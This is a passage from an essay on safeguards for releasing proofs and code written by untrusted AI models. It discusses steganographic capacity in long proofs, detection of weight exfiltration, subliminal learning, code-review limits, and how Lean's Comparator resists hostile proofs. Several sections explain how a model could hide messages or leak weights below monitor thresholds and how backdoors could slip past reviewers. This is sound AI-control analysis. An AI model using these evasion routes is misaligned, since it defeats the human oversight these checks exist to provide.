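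These results probably understate what a laboratory should now expect. Average accuracy on the number-hiding task rose from 43% with Claude Opus 4 to 55% with Opus 4.5, and all the models in the study predate GPT-6 Astra. Karpov also made the models do the encoding unaided. An agent that can run code could write a small program to do the encoding, although this would leave a record that the laboratory could inspect.

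Deliberately training a model to hide messages makes it do so more reliably. In *Now You (Still) See Me* (2026), researchers trained models to hide 32 bits in their output, which lowered their scores on standard tests of ability by an average of between 0.8% and 6.4%. In the first of two experiments, detectors that examine a model's internal activity caught all of these models, with the threshold set to allow 5% false alarms. These detectors need the model's weights, so only the laboratory can run them in an artifact-only release.

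### How much fits in a long proof?

If each of the Riemann proof's 17 million lines offered one free choice between two equally natural options, the file could carry a hidden message of 17 million bits, or about 2.1 megabytes. One bit per line is a modest assumption, because the order of ten import lines alone can encode 21 bits.

The largest secret a model could try to send is a copy of its own weights, which might occupy a terabyte, but a thief can compress them first. In *Aggressive Compression Enables LLM Weight Theft*, Brown, Rivera and colleagues (2026) compressed a model with 1.5 billion weights to a sixteenth of its size. After some retraining, its accuracy on a broad test of knowledge was only 1.6% lower. They estimate that thieves could compress models by up to 100 times, partly because larger models seem easier to compress.

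| Hidden content | Size | Lines needed at one bit per line | Files of 17 million lines |
|---|---|---|---|
| Encryption key | 256 bits | 256 | a tiny part of one |
| 1,000 words of instructions | about 6 kilobytes | about 48,000 | 0.3% of one |
| Weights, compressed 100 times | 10 gigabytes | 80 billion | about 4,700 |
| Weights, compressed 16 times | 62.5 gigabytes | 500 billion | about 29,000 |
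| Weights, uncompressed | 1 terabyte | 8 trillion | about 470,000 |

Nobody is likely to smuggle a whole model out in proofs, but a key or a set of instructions would fit easily. Shortening the file doesn't help much. At the same rate, the 76,000-line version of the Riemann proof could still hold 9.5 kilobytes, enough for a key and about 1,500 words.

### Detecting leaks of a model's weights

A thief who wants the model's weights would do better to hide them in the output of a busy chat service, which sends out far more data than an occasional proof. At each step, the model assigns probabilities to the possible next tokens (words or parts of words), and the server's software uses pseudorandom numbers to pick one. An attacker who controls the server can instead pick tokens that encode the weights, while the answers still read normally.

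*Verifying LLM Inference to Detect Model Weight Exfiltration* (Rinberg, Karvonen and colleagues, 2025) describes a defence in which the provider records the seed, the starting value that determines the pseudorandom numbers, and reruns a random sample of requests on a separate trusted computer. If the server is honest, the rerun should produce the same token almost every time. Small rounding differences can change the choice when two tokens are nearly tied, so some mismatches are innocent, and a careful attacker has to disguise stolen data as these mismatches. On a model with 30 billion weights, the method reduced the share of the output that could carry stolen data to less than 0.5%. At that rate, stealing a one-terabyte model would take more than 200 days instead of about a day.

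A patient attacker could leak so little in each answer that no single answer looks suspicious. In *Anytime-valid detection of LLM weight exfiltration*, Ortega-Fernandez, Kowalczyk and Warr (2026) therefore keep a running score across answers. The score rises when a mismatch is hard to explain by rounding and can fall after a normal answer. They set the alarm threshold so that the chance of ever raising a false alarm stays below 1%, however long monitoring lasts, provided that normal traffic stays like the traffic used for calibration.

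In simulated runs of 250 answers on four models, the method caught every attacker who didn't know the seed, after a median of 6 to 14 answers depending on the model. Attackers who knew the seed could limit themselves to near-ties, and on one model they escaped detection in every run while leaking 0.03 bits per token. At that rate, leaking a terabyte would take about 260 trillion tokens, but leaking a 256-bit key would take only about 8,400.

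Rerunning the model on a trusted computer exposes a tampered server, but it can't expose a message that the model itself wrote, because the rerun would produce the same message. Rinberg and colleagues say that their method does not cover a model that reveals its weights as intended behaviour. The check can show that nobody altered a file after an untrusted model wrote it, but it gives no reason to trust the model.

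A limit on how much data leaves the building works no matter who sends it. As *Haiku to Opus in Just 10 bits* (2026) points out, if only 10 gigabytes leave a data centre, nobody can steal more than 10 gigabytes from it that way. A chat service may struggle with a strict limit because its customers need answers, but a laboratory that releases a few proofs a month can easily accept one. The laboratory should account for compression when setting the limit, because a one-terabyte model compressed by a factor of 100 would fit in 10 gigabytes.

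### Traits that pass through training data

A model can also pick up a trait from another model's output when nobody has deliberately encoded anything. Alex Cloud and colleagues reported this effect in 2025 and called it subliminal learning. *You Didn't Have to Say it like That* (Gisler, He and Qiu, 2026) describes the original experiment. The researchers told one copy of a model, the teacher, that it loved owls, and asked it to produce sequences of numbers. They filtered out anything that referred to the trait, trained another copy, the student, on the remaining numbers, and asked about its favourite animal. The student chose owls 48 percentage points more often than the original model. Teachers trained to behave badly also passed on some of their bad behaviour, even after the researchers removed numbers with negative associations.

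Filtering failed because the trait was not in the visible content. Many numbers can continue a sequence equally well, and the instruction to love owls slightly changes which ones the teacher picks. No single number is suspicious, so a filter for references to owls has nothing to remove.

The student can absorb this pattern as a preference because it starts with the same weights as the teacher. Suppose that giving the teacher its preference amounts to changing those weights by t, a long list of small adjustments, and that training on the teacher's numbers changes the student's weights by δ. As Hatami, Aalishah and Monosov (2026) explain in *Subliminal Learning in Vision-Language Models*, the squared distance between student and teacher then changes by

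|δ|² − 2(δ · t)

The product δ · t is positive when the two changes point even partly in the same direction. A small enough step then brings the student closer to the teacher, which tends to strengthen the preference as well. According to *Defence against the dark arts of distillation* (Egan, Gilligan-Lee and colleagues, 2026), Cloud and colleagues proved that a single, small enough training step on any output of the teacher moves the student towards the teacher, whatever the output is about.

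That reason for a student to move towards its teacher does not apply when the two start with different weights. In *Subliminal Learning Is Steering Vector Distillation* (2026), researchers trained students based on the model Qwen on numbers from teachers based on another model, OLMo. The students' preferences for cats, dogs and tigers did not rise above their original levels. Gisler and colleagues mention one experiment in which a trait did pass between different models through ordinary prose, but the filters had left some visible associations with the trait in the text.

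Later experiments found the effect in other kinds of data. Gisler and colleagues had a teacher model that favored dolphins paraphrase sentences about unrelated subjects, and discarded any paraphrase that changed the meaning. Students trained on the rest chose dolphins 19 percentage points more often than students of a neutral teacher. When the sentences insulted dolphins, the increase was still 18 points. The effect was strong for only two of the five animals tested, dolphins and eagles. Hatami and colleagues found increases of up to about 10 points in models that process images. *Slow Decay and Silenced Expression* (2026) followed three chains in which each model trained on the filtered output of the one before, and all three still showed the trait in the tenth generation.

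Researchers disagree about how robust the effect is. Nief, Fu and colleagues (2026), in *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact*, found that it disappeared when training adjusted all of a model's weights instead of a small set of added ones. It mostly disappeared when the standing instructions at the top of the prompt differed between training and testing, and they did not find it at all in Llama 3.1. Morgulis and Hewitt (2026), in *Subliminal Steering*, found that the original method worked on only one of four models. But when they gave the teacher its preference by directly altering its internal activity, instead of by an instruction, the trait also passed to Llama and Phi models, even when training adjusted all the weights. The effect may be fragile because of the way experimenters usually create the trait. It is unclear which method better represents a goal that a model acquires in ordinary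 training.

In an artifact-only release, most outsiders don't have a model with the same starting weights, unless the laboratory built its private model from an open one. The laboratory faces more risk because it may train the model's next version on the current version's programs and proofs.

Egan and colleagues offer a way to look for an inherited trait without knowing what it is. They train the same base model separately on several datasets from one teacher and compare how the weights change. The changes that reflect task skills should differ between datasets, while the change that carries the trait should be much the same. They isolate this shared change and amplify it until the model mentions the trait in answers to unrelated questions, then remove the change from the model. In their tests, this revealed the animal preferences, and removing them had almost no effect on task performance.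 The method assumes that the datasets vary and that the trait is unrelated to the tasks. The second assumption might fail for a habit of writing slightly insecure code if all the data were code.

### Removing hidden messages before release

A laboratory can destroy a hidden message without finding it by removing the choices that could carry it. For example, sorting a program's import lines alphabetically leaves only one possible order. Automatic formatters do the same for spacing and line breaks with almost no effort. Replacing variable names with standard ones and deleting comments removes more of these choices, but makes the code harder to review and maintain. The laboratory's own reviewers can still work from the original, but outsiders would have only the stripped version.

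Reformatting a program doesn't change deeper choices, such as which algorithm it uses. No tool can reduce every program to a standard form that depends only on its behaviour, because such a tool could decide whether any two programs behave identically, which Rice's theorem rules out. Changing only part of a program may not remove a hidden message, because a sender can repeat the message so that it survives some damage.

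Someone could instead rewrite the whole program from its specification. This removes nearly all the original author's choices, but it takes a lot of work and can introduce new mistakes, so the laboratory would have to repeat its tests and proofs. It also replaces the author's choices with the rewriter's. In the dolphin experiment, the trait came from the model that paraphrased the sentences, although another model had written them. An untrusted model should therefore not rewrite its own work, and a weaker model that the laboratory trusts more would be a better choice.

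An inert export of a formal proof is a plain-data copy that a checker reads without running the author's code. It leaves out comments, spacing and the commands Lean used to construct each step, so none of these can hide a message. But it keeps the logical steps, the author's choice of intermediate results and the names of those results, all of which can still carry one.

Someone who only needs to know that a theorem is true can check the proof on an isolated computer, keep the verdict and delete the file. If people fixed the theorem's statement in advance, the verdict carries at most one bit of information. But mathematicians then can't learn from the proof, and others have to trust whoever ran the check.

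Anyone who needs the artifact itself can't realistically rule out a hidden message as short as a 256-bit key. The laboratory can limit what such a message could reveal by never giving the model passwords, keys or access to its own weights. It can also avoid training new models on the artifacts, although it would lose a cheap source of high-quality data. Keeping artifacts out of training becomes harder after publication, because copies spread across the web and may enter later models' training data unless someone labels them and filters them out.

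## How much can human and AI reviewers check?

Many of the precautions above depend on a reviewer reading what a model has written and noticing the unexplained constant, the opaque test file or the missing length limit. Rules of thumb from before AI coding tools often put careful review at 200 to 400 lines of code an hour. These figures are too old to describe today's reviewers, but they give a sense of scale. At that speed, reading the 17 million lines of the Riemann proof would take 42,500 to 85,000 hours, or about 21 to 43 years for someone working 2,000 hours a year.

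Hardly anyone reviews full-time, though. In a survey of developers at a large software company, the median respondent spent 6 to 10 hours a week on review (Newman, Bird and colleagues, 2026, *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices*). At that rate, a developer would need 85 to 283 years to read the whole proof. The 76,000-line version would take 190 to 380 hours.

Proof checkers spare people from checking by hand, but most generated software comes without a proof. People who want to rely on it have to read it or find another reason to trust it.

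### More code and longer queues

Programmers usually submit new code as a pull request, a set of proposed changes that colleagues review before it becomes part of the program. AI agents have made these changes larger and more frequent. Adams, Banga and colleagues report in *Automating Low-Risk Code Review at Meta* (2026) that lines per change at Meta grew by 105.9% in a year and changes per developer by 51%. These increases imply that each developer produced about three times as many lines to review. The share of changes reviewed within 24 hours fell, and some large groups had thousands of changes waiting for review.

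*Artificial Intelligence in the Firm* (Chen and Stratton, 2026) compares firms that had just adopted AI tools with firms that had not yet done so, using records from Jellyfish, a company whose software tracks the work of engineering teams. In the August version, which covers 718 firms, coding agents increased the number of lines written by 30% and the number of pull requests by 23%. The number of completed tasks rose by at most 12%, and may not have risen at all.

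*Code Review Is the Bottleneck. That's the Good News* (Woodruff, 2026) describes a November version of a study by economists, which covers 720,542 engineers at 655 firms. After firms adopted agents, lines of code rose by 44% and completed tasks rose by 13.7%, though the result for tasks was borderline. The time from submitting a change to getting approval rose by 56.1%. Changes waited longer for a reviewer, who then spent longer on them and left 38.6% more comments. The economists estimate that firms used 22.7% less labour for coding and 43.4% more for review. The number of bug reports per developer did not change significantly.

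Reviewers at these firms therefore seem to have maintained quality by slowing down. Woodruff, who writes about software, had expected them to approve changes with little scrutiny and says the study proved him wrong. He adds that firms willing to pay for this kind of tracking may be more disciplined than most, and that counting bug reports is not the same as counting serious failures.

At one company, review did become more superficial. *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) followed 802 developers and 196,212 pull requests from January 2024 to April 2026. In June 2025 the company's chief technology officer told staff to double the number of accepted pull requests per engineer within a year, and they had nearly done so by the tenth month. Each reviewer then handled about twice as many changes as before. Human reviewers increasingly approved changes without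 comment, and automated review soon covered more changes than human review did. The share of changes that developers later reversed stayed flat. The study covers a single company with an explicit output target, so it is weaker evidence about typical behaviour than the Jellyfish data, but it shows what can happen when managers reward the quantity of accepted code.

Companies can't easily fix the shortage by hiring. In the November data, 82.8% of reviews came from someone who already knew the code in question, and a new employee takes time to learn it. A large program that an AI model delivers complete is even harder to review, because at first no human knows any of it.

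These studies measure how much review people do. They provide little evidence of how many planted flaws get through, because bug reports and reversals include only faults that somebody noticed. The XZ backdoor would not have appeared in either until Freund investigated his slow logins.

### Reviewers miss flaws that they know how to recognise

In experiments, developers often overlook a common security flaw that they would recognise if they were looking for one. *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021) describes a test in which developers reviewed code that failed to check what users typed into it, then looked again after a warning that the code was vulnerable. One of the flaws allowed SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a form and the program carries them out. Most participants identified this well-known flaw, but some only after the warning.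 One said of the first review, "I was looking mainly for good programming practices".

A general instruction can help reviewers even if it doesn't reveal that a flaw is present. Braz and Aeberhard (2022), in *Less is More*, ran an online experiment with 150 participants, 71% of whom had at least three years of professional experience. Asking them to focus on security made them eight times as likely to detect a vulnerability. Adding a security checklist did not significantly improve detection further, even when the researchers tailored it to the flaws in the code.

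A laboratory can easily give its reviewers the same instruction. It shouldn't expect the full benefit, because these experiments used well-known types of flaw and left them undisguised. Participants also reviewed a small amount of code in one session, whereas a laboratory's reviewers might read clean code for months before they meet a planted flaw, and may become less attentive. Flaws in less familiar places could be even harder to spot. *Architectural Backdoors in Vision-Language Model Supply Chains via Representation Steering* (Briglia, Maljkovic and colleagues, 2026) cites earlier studies in which people had difficulty detecting backdoors in the code that defines a neural network's structure.

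### The odds of catching a planted flaw

If reviewers read only part of a program, their chance of catching a flaw depends on how much they read and how carefully. Suppose that they read a randomly chosen fraction f of the program, and that they notice a flaw in what they read with probability d. They then catch a single planted flaw with probability

f × d

Reviewers who read 5% of a program and notice 60% of the flaws in what they read have a 5% × 60% = 3% chance of catching a given flaw. Reading 5% of a 17-million-line program would take one person between one and two years at the old rule-of-thumb speed.

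Reviewers have to choose the sample at random, after the model has delivered its work. If the model can predict which files they will read, it can put the flaw in another file, where they have no chance of finding it. Jia Tan used a similar tactic by keeping the XZ script out of the public repository.

Sampling works much better against an author who plants many flaws. If the program contains k flaws and reviewers have an independent chance of catching each one, they catch at least one with probability

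1 − (1 − f × d)^k

With the same 3% chance per flaw, reviewers would find at least one of 100 flaws about 95% of the time. Sampling can therefore expose a model that routinely writes bad code, but it will probably miss a model that plants one backdoor and otherwise behaves well.

Some flaws will remain even if reviewers read everything. If a laboratory releases N artifacts, a proportion p of them contain a flaw, and reviewers detect each flaw with probability d, the expected number that they miss is

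N × p × (1 − d)

Suppose that 10 of 10,000 programs contain a backdoor, and reviewers detect 80% of the backdoors in the code they read. If they read every program in full, they will miss about two. If they read only 5% of each program, they will miss between nine and ten on average. Missing two backdoors may be acceptable if the programs sort photographs, but not if they control a power grid.

False alarms also use up reviewers' time. If the reviewers in this example wrongly flag 1% of the clean programs, someone has to investigate about 100 of those along with the eight that contain backdoors, so about 93% of the flagged programs are harmless. After months of this, people may start to dismiss alarms too quickly, which lowers d.

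The hardest number to estimate is p, because nobody knows how often an untrusted model plants flaws. A laboratory can estimate d by adding known flaws to some programs and counting how many its reviewers find. The estimate will be too high if a hostile model can hide flaws better than the laboratory's testers can.

### What AI reviewers find

AI reviewers can read far more code than people can. Yang, He and colleagues (2026), in *(When) Should a Software Factory be Lights-off?*, measured how well AI reviewers detect bugs. They collected bugs that developers had found and fixed, and traced each one back to the change that introduced it. They then asked AI agents to review the program as it stood at that time, without telling them that it contained a bug. An agent succeeded if the bug appeared among its five highest-ranked comments.

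On 1,000 such changes from 98 public projects, the best agent, which used Claude Opus 5 (July 2026), found 71.9% of the bugs. An agent using Claude Opus 4.6 (February 2026) found 47.7%, so current models may well do better. Opus 5 took an average of 9.8 minutes and cost $2.97 per review. The median change was 189 lines, so an AI review of 17 million lines would cost very roughly $270,000. Agents working in parallel can finish such a review in days.

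Several of the agents' weaknesses would matter more if the author were hostile:

- They did worse on larger changes, and a model can easily write large ones.
- They were much better at finding bugs visible in the changed lines than bugs that, like the XZ backdoor, required knowledge of other files or of how the program runs.
- They sometimes believed misleading comments and descriptions. An untrusted model writes its own comments, so a laboratory could remove them from the copy it gives to an AI reviewer.
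- They rarely ran the code. Even Opus 5 did so in only 9.7% of its steps.

Performance also fell by up to 25.5% on two large private projects from one company, partly because fewer of the bugs there were visible in the changed lines. A laboratory therefore has to test an AI reviewer on the laboratory's own code to learn how well it works there. Yang and colleagues recommend that companies build such tests from their own past bugs.

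More computation improves AI code review somewhat. Asking agents to explore the code more thoroughly improved results by up to 5.8% and raised the cost by about 10%. Using several agents for each review improved results by 4.7% but cost more than five times as much.

AI reviewers may be especially useful for finding logic bugs, in which a program breaks an unwritten rule about how it should behave. For example, an online shop might let a customer apply the same discount code twice. The program doesn't crash, so a fuzzer that detects only crashes will miss the bug. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) compared four ways of using language models to look for such bugs and found that the simplest methods worked best. A backdoor also breaks a rule without causing a crash, but logic bugs are honest mistakes that nobody has tried to hide, so success at finding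 them is only indirect evidence that AI reviewers can find backdoors.

Finding more bugs doesn't necessarily save people any work. Yang and colleagues describe an earlier experiment in which expert developers received AI-written reviews. The developers found more low-severity problems, but they did not find more high-severity ones, finish faster or feel more confident.

Newman and colleagues found a similar result at the large software company, where they interviewed 24 developers and received 2,590 usable survey responses in July and August 2026. Respondents who used AI for review did not report less difficulty keeping up with the volume of changes. AI review may still help, because the developers with the most to review may also be the most likely to try it, and only 9% of the people invited gave usable responses. One explanation for the result is that human reviewers now do different work.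 Among respondents who could compare with the time before AI-written code, 71% said they had shifted towards higher-level questions such as a change's design and purpose, and 56% said they spent more effort checking whether it addressed the right problem.

### When two reviewers make the same mistake

A natural response to missed flaws is to add a second reviewer. Suppose that each of two reviewers misses 20% of flaws. If their mistakes are independent, they both miss a given flaw with probability 20% × 20% = 4%. If they always miss the same flaws, the second reviewer adds nothing and the figure stays at 20%. For cases in between, let m be the proportion that each reviewer misses and ρ the correlation between their misses, from 0 for independent mistakes to 1 for identical ones. The probability that both miss a flaw is

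m² + ρ × m × (1 − m)

With a correlation of 0.5, the two reviewers jointly miss 12% of flaws, three times as many as independent reviewers would.

Reviewers who never communicate can still make correlated mistakes, because some flaws are harder to see than others. Suppose half of all flaws are obvious enough that everyone finds them, and each reviewer misses 40% of the hard ones. Each reviewer then misses 20% of all flaws. Two reviewers working separately both miss 16% of the hard flaws, which is 8% of all flaws, rather than the 4% expected if their mistakes were uncorrelated.

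The results from Yang and colleagues show this pattern. Human reviewers had caught half of the bugs in their public collection before the code change was accepted, and had missed the other half. Opus 5 missed 20.4% of the bugs that the humans had caught and 35.8% of those they had missed. Together, humans and Opus 5 would have found 82.1% of the bugs, compared with about 86% if their mistakes had been independent. The difference is fairly small, so combining human and AI review is still worthwhile. However, the true overlap between their mistakes could be larger, because the collection contains only bugs that somebody eventually noticed.

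Engineers learned about correlated mistakes decades ago, when they tried to make software more reliable through N-version programming. Several teams write the same program, the versions run side by side, and the majority answer is used. This works best if the versions fail on different inputs. In 1986, John Knight and Nancy Leveson tested whether they do by comparing versions that programmers had written independently from one specification. The versions failed on the same inputs significantly more often than independent failures would explain, as *N-Version Programming with Coding Agents* (2026) recounts. *A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) attributes this to programmers reading an ambiguous specification in the same way, choosing similar designs and reasoning alike.

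Knight and Leveson studied people who wrote programs, but reviewers can go wrong for the same reasons. If a specification doesn't cover bank transfers for negative amounts, several reviewers may all overlook that case.

AI reviewers could have even more in common than human programmers do. Two copies of one model share all their weights, and different models have often learned from much of the same text. An untrusted model that reviews its own work could also recognise a flaw that it planted and not report it. Despite this, in a survey of 377 engineers and managers, 47% said that their organisations rely on AI agents to review code that those agents wrote (Kerner, *AI coding agents are reviewing their own code*, 2026). A company that sells AI code review sponsored the survey, so the exact figure deserves some caution.

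A laboratory can make shared mistakes less likely by combining different kinds of checks, such as a human reviewer, a model from another developer and an ordinary program that searches for known flaws. These checks may still miss some of the same flaws, but they don't have to be fully independent to be useful. In the earlier example with a correlation of 0.5, adding a second reviewer reduced the proportion of missed flaws from 20% to 12%.

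### Reducing what people must read

Companies have strong financial reasons to make review faster. Woodruff reports a simulation by Chen and Stratton in which software output rises by 57.8% by 2031 if review continues at its current pace, and by 341.4% if review speeds up as quickly as coding. A manager could seek the larger gain by approving changes with less scrutiny, and it might be months before anyone noticed the harm. Several other methods reduce how much reviewers have to read with less risk, though each has a drawback.

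A laboratory can ask for shorter artifacts. The shorter Riemann proof would take less than 1% as long to read as the original. But somebody has to produce a shorter version and check it again, and very compact code can take longer to understand per line. A laboratory can also release fewer artifacts, but it then loses whatever benefit the others would have brought.

Authors can do more of the work before review. Developers in the study by Newman and colleagues rated this among the most helpful strategies. The researchers recommend that authors revise their code with an AI reviewer before submitting it. An AI model could also divide its work into small changes and supply tests and an explanation for each. This mainly uses computing time, which costs less than human reviewers' time. But reviewers can't assume that an untrusted model's explanations are true, and a backdoor spread across several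 small changes may be harder to see than one in a single file.

Another option is to have people read only the riskiest changes. Meta's system, RADAR, estimates how likely each change is to cause a serious failure, and an AI reviewer then looks for signs of danger. RADAR can approve an eligible change without human review if the estimated risk is low, the AI reviewer is confident that it is safe, and it passes the automatic tests. By the time of Adams and colleagues' paper, RADAR had reviewed more than 535,000 changes and put over 331,000 into use. Developers later reversed these changes a third as often as others, and the changes caused serious failures a fiftieth as often. This comparison makes RADAR look better than it is, because it selects changes that were already unlikely to cause trouble.

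Meta designed RADAR mainly to catch accidents, and a hostile author could try to make a dangerous change look routine. For example, the AI reviewer treats added tests as a sign of safety, but the XZ attacker hid the harmful code in test files. Meta does block automatic approval for some kinds of AI-written change, including tasks with "test" in their names. A laboratory that sorts an untrusted model's work by risk could also send a random sample of the apparently safe changes to human reviewers, so that no category is certain to escape human review. This uses up some of the time that the sorting saved.

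Reviewers can avoid reading most of a program if it comes with a machine-checked proof that it has the properties they need. They still have to read the specification very carefully, but it is often much shorter than the code. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes how Claude proved security properties of 123 open-source libraries.

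## How can a machine-checked proof be trusted when its author is not?

A formal proof is an argument written in a language precise enough for a program, called a proof checker, to check every step. The checker only confirms that each step follows the rules. Its result doesn't depend on who wrote the proof, so people can accept a proof from a model they don't trust.

### What a kernel checks

In Lean, every mathematical statement is a type, meaning a kind of object, and a proof of the statement is an object of that type. Lean users call this object a proof term. Freer and Subramanian (2026), in *Lean*, illustrate the idea with a very small theorem, which one can write like this:

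```
theorem swap (p q : Prop) (h : p ∧ q) : q ∧ p := ⟨h.right, h.left⟩
```

The part before the := sign is the statement. In words, for any propositions p and q, anyone who has a proof h of "p and q" can prove "q and p". The part after the sign is the proof term, a pair that contains the two halves of h in reverse order.

Lean's kernel, which checks proofs, goes through the term piece by piece. Since h proves "p and q", its right half proves q and its left half proves p. Pairing them in that order proves "q and p", which matches the statement, so the kernel accepts the proof. If the author had forgotten to swap the halves, the pair would prove "p and q" instead, and the kernel would reject it.

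Nobody writes a long proof entirely in this form. Authors use tactics, which are programs that search for and assemble a proof term. Bugs in a tactic or thousands of false starts by an AI model do no harm, because the kernel checks the final term. Freer and Subramanian report that the official kernel has about 8,000 lines of code. By an old rule of thumb for code review, someone could read it in 20 to 40 hours, and the same kernel checks every proof.

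### Why the author's honesty stops mattering

If a user fixes the statement, the rules of the logic and the checker before the proof arrives, the verdict depends only on the proof term. An honest mathematician and a hostile model who submit the same term get the same verdict. As long as the rules never lead to a false conclusion and the checker applies them correctly, a hostile author can waste the user's computing time but can't get a false statement accepted.

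Langley (2026) points out in *We have proof automation now* that once the statement is correct, in theory it matters only that a proof exists. In practice, the proof's contents can still cause trouble. For example, a complicated proof can make a checker use vast amounts of memory.

Lean's rules are close to those that mathematicians already rely on. The usual foundation of mathematics is ZFC, a list of axioms about sets. ZFC can be extended by adding infinitely many "strongly inaccessible cardinals", which are infinite sizes so large that ZFC alone can't prove they exist. Earlier work showed that Lean's rules are free of contradiction exactly if this extended ZFC is. *Reflections on Trusting Lean* (Bresolin and Mamino, 2026) goes further and proves that the two systems have exactly the same theorems about whole numbers and sets of whole numbers.

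Some theorems require even less trust in the rules. Fermat's Last Theorem states that no positive whole numbers a, b and c satisfy aⁿ + bⁿ = cⁿ for any whole number n greater than 2. If it were false, there would be a counterexample, which Lean could verify by arithmetic. If Lean also accepted a proof of the theorem, its rules would contradict themselves. So to trust a Lean proof of the theorem, a reader only has to believe that the rules are consistent.

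### From source files to a verdict

Authors normally send source files, and a hostile author could interfere at several points between those files and the verdict. The Lean Language Reference's *Validating a Lean Proof* groups unreviewed AI-generated proofs with deliberate attacks. It recommends checking them with Lean's *Comparator*, which covers every step from the source files to the verdict.

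People read a proof's source, and its author can make that source misleading. The Lean community's *Did you prove it?* warns that anyone can give a complicated statement the name TheRiemannHypothesis, whatever the statement means. An author can also redefine the whole numbers or basic operations on them, so that a familiar-looking line means something else. Careful reading is a weak defence in a large project, because the redefinition could be in any of thousands of files. Comparing the theorem with a trusted statement at the end protects the user better.

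Compiling a Lean proof runs its author's code, because authors can write their own tactics and the compiler has to run them to produce the proof terms. A malicious tactic could delete the user's files or change the file that contains the trusted statement. It could also interfere with Lean itself. According to the Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.1* (2026), code that runs in the same process as the kernel has crude ways to get a bad proof accepted. If the author is hostile, error-free compilation and the blue check marks that Lean shows beside finished theorems are therefore weak evidence that the proof is valid.

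Comparator compiles the author's files in a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits what a running program can read, change or contact. According to its instructions, Comparator also depends on the user never having compiled those files outside the sandbox, because a single earlier compilation could have altered the trusted statement.

Lean stores proof terms in compiled files, which it loads straight into memory to save time. An attacker could craft a file with invalid memory addresses to take control of the program that opens it. An older tool, lean4checker, reads the stored terms and runs them through the kernel again. This catches theorems that a tactic added without a check, but the Lean Language Reference notes that the tool doesn't verify the format of the compiled files. Comparator doesn't load these files itself.

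A separate program in a sandbox reads the compiled files and exports the definitions, statements and proof terms as plain data. The kernel may have to do calculations within the logic while it checks this data, but those calculations can't open a file or contact a network. Malicious code could still tamper with the export while the sandboxed program writes it, but the author would gain nothing, because the kernel checks the export itself and any altered entry would also have to be a valid proof.

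Comparator then checks the exported terms with the official kernel and, optionally, with nanoda, a kernel that another developer wrote in Rust. By this stage, a hostile author would need a bug in every kernel the user runs to get an invalid proof accepted.

The kernel accepts anything that follows from the axioms, and authors can add axioms of their own. Someone could declare the Riemann hypothesis as an axiom and then "prove" it in one line. Lean also has a placeholder, `sorry`, that stands in for a missing proof. The user can detect both by listing the axioms that a theorem depends on. Most proofs need only Lean's three standard ones:

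- Two statements that imply each other count as equal.
- Objects that a definition treats as equivalent become equal in the new collection it creates. For example, the pairs 1/2 and 2/4 become the same fraction.
- From any collection that isn't empty, one can choose an element without specifying which.

Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) shows why the list of axioms matters. The security company produced a bogus proof, only a few lines long, that received Lean's blue check marks. It relied on a function that extracts part of a text. If that part was at an enormously distant position, the function's logical definition gave an empty text, but the compiled version gave the whole original. The proof used a feature that lets compiled code settle a step, so it could show that an empty text equals a non-empty one. Any statement can be proved from such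 a contradiction, including Fermat's Last Theorem. But the feature adds an axiom, so the list had four entries instead of three.

Finally, Comparator checks the theorem against a statement that the user trusts. The user puts this statement in a "challenge" file, with `sorry` in place of the proof. The author's theorem and every definition it uses must match those in the challenge file, down to the basic definitions built into Lean, so Comparator would reject a proof whose author had redefined the whole numbers.

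The comparison works less well if the challenge leaves a blank for the author to fill in. Suppose a user wants to know whether the Riemann hypothesis is true, and asks for a proof that "the Riemann hypothesis holds if and only if X", where the author chooses X. The author can choose the Riemann hypothesis itself as X, which makes the proof trivial. Lean's documentation therefore tells users to have a person or another program judge every answer of this kind.

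### Kevin Buzzard's four questions

Many people hear only that someone has "checked" a proof in Lean. On 12 November 2026 Kevin Buzzard, who runs a project that teaches mathematicians to use Lean, explained how to interpret such claims in the Xena Project's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026). He proposed four questions, which amount to the following:

1. Does the formal statement mean the same as the theorem in ordinary language?
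2. Does the code compile?
3. Does the code prove that statement?
4. Does the proof pass only because it exploits a bug in the official kernel?

Computers can mostly answer the last three questions, but the one about meaning needs someone who knows both Lean and the mathematics. Buzzard's example is a short definition named FermatsLastTheorem, which states that aⁿ + bⁿ never equals cⁿ for natural numbers a, b, c and n, with n at least 3. Lean's natural numbers include zero, so a = b = c = 0 with n = 3 is a counterexample. The definition still compiles, since compiling a statement only shows that it is meaningful. No proof of it could compile, so this mistake would be noticed. A statement that is accidentally too easy to prove is more dangerous, because a proof of it could compile.

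Published code may also prove something other than the main result. Buzzard counted about 38 such cases among the 290 theorems that OpenAI released with Lean code in October, although OpenAI had not claimed that the code in those cases proved the main result.

*The Footprint Moved*, from the website Artificial Wasteland, describes a small test of the four questions. The AI agents that write the site applied the questions to the 26 Lean files behind its pages. Two files no longer compiled under the newest version of Lean, but once they were repaired, six kernels accepted all 26. Thirteen statements on the site claimed more than the files proved. The proofs held up better than the site's descriptions of them, though the agents were auditing their own site and may have missed some errors.

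The audit also found that a theorem's list of axioms can change for a harmless reason. Eight theorems gained an axiom under the newest version of Lean because it proved a basic fact about numbers differently. The added axiom was one of Lean's three standard axioms, so the theorems were as secure as before.

### How people checked the Riemann proof

Alpöge released his proof eight days after Buzzard's post. It has 17 million lines in 175,187 modules (Lean source files) and proves five theorems. One is the Riemann hypothesis, stated exactly as it already was in Mathlib. In words, if the Riemann zeta function is zero at a complex number s, and s is neither a negative even number nor 1, then the real part of s is ½.

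Artificial Wasteland's *The Twenty Lines* explains what each exception is for. The zeta function is zero at −2, −4 and every other negative even number, so the hypothesis would be false without the first exception. At s = 1 the function has no value, but Lean requires every function to have a value everywhere, and Mathlib's construction happens to give about −0.977 there. Buzzard and Jordan Ellenberg pointed out that an early version of the formal statement had no exception for 1. The exception turned out to make no difference, since −0.977 isn't zero.

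The other four theorems restate the hypothesis and extend it to a larger family, the Dirichlet L-functions. Mathlib did not already contain the extended versions, so experts have to read them more carefully. But all five theorems and the definitions written for them take up only about twenty lines.

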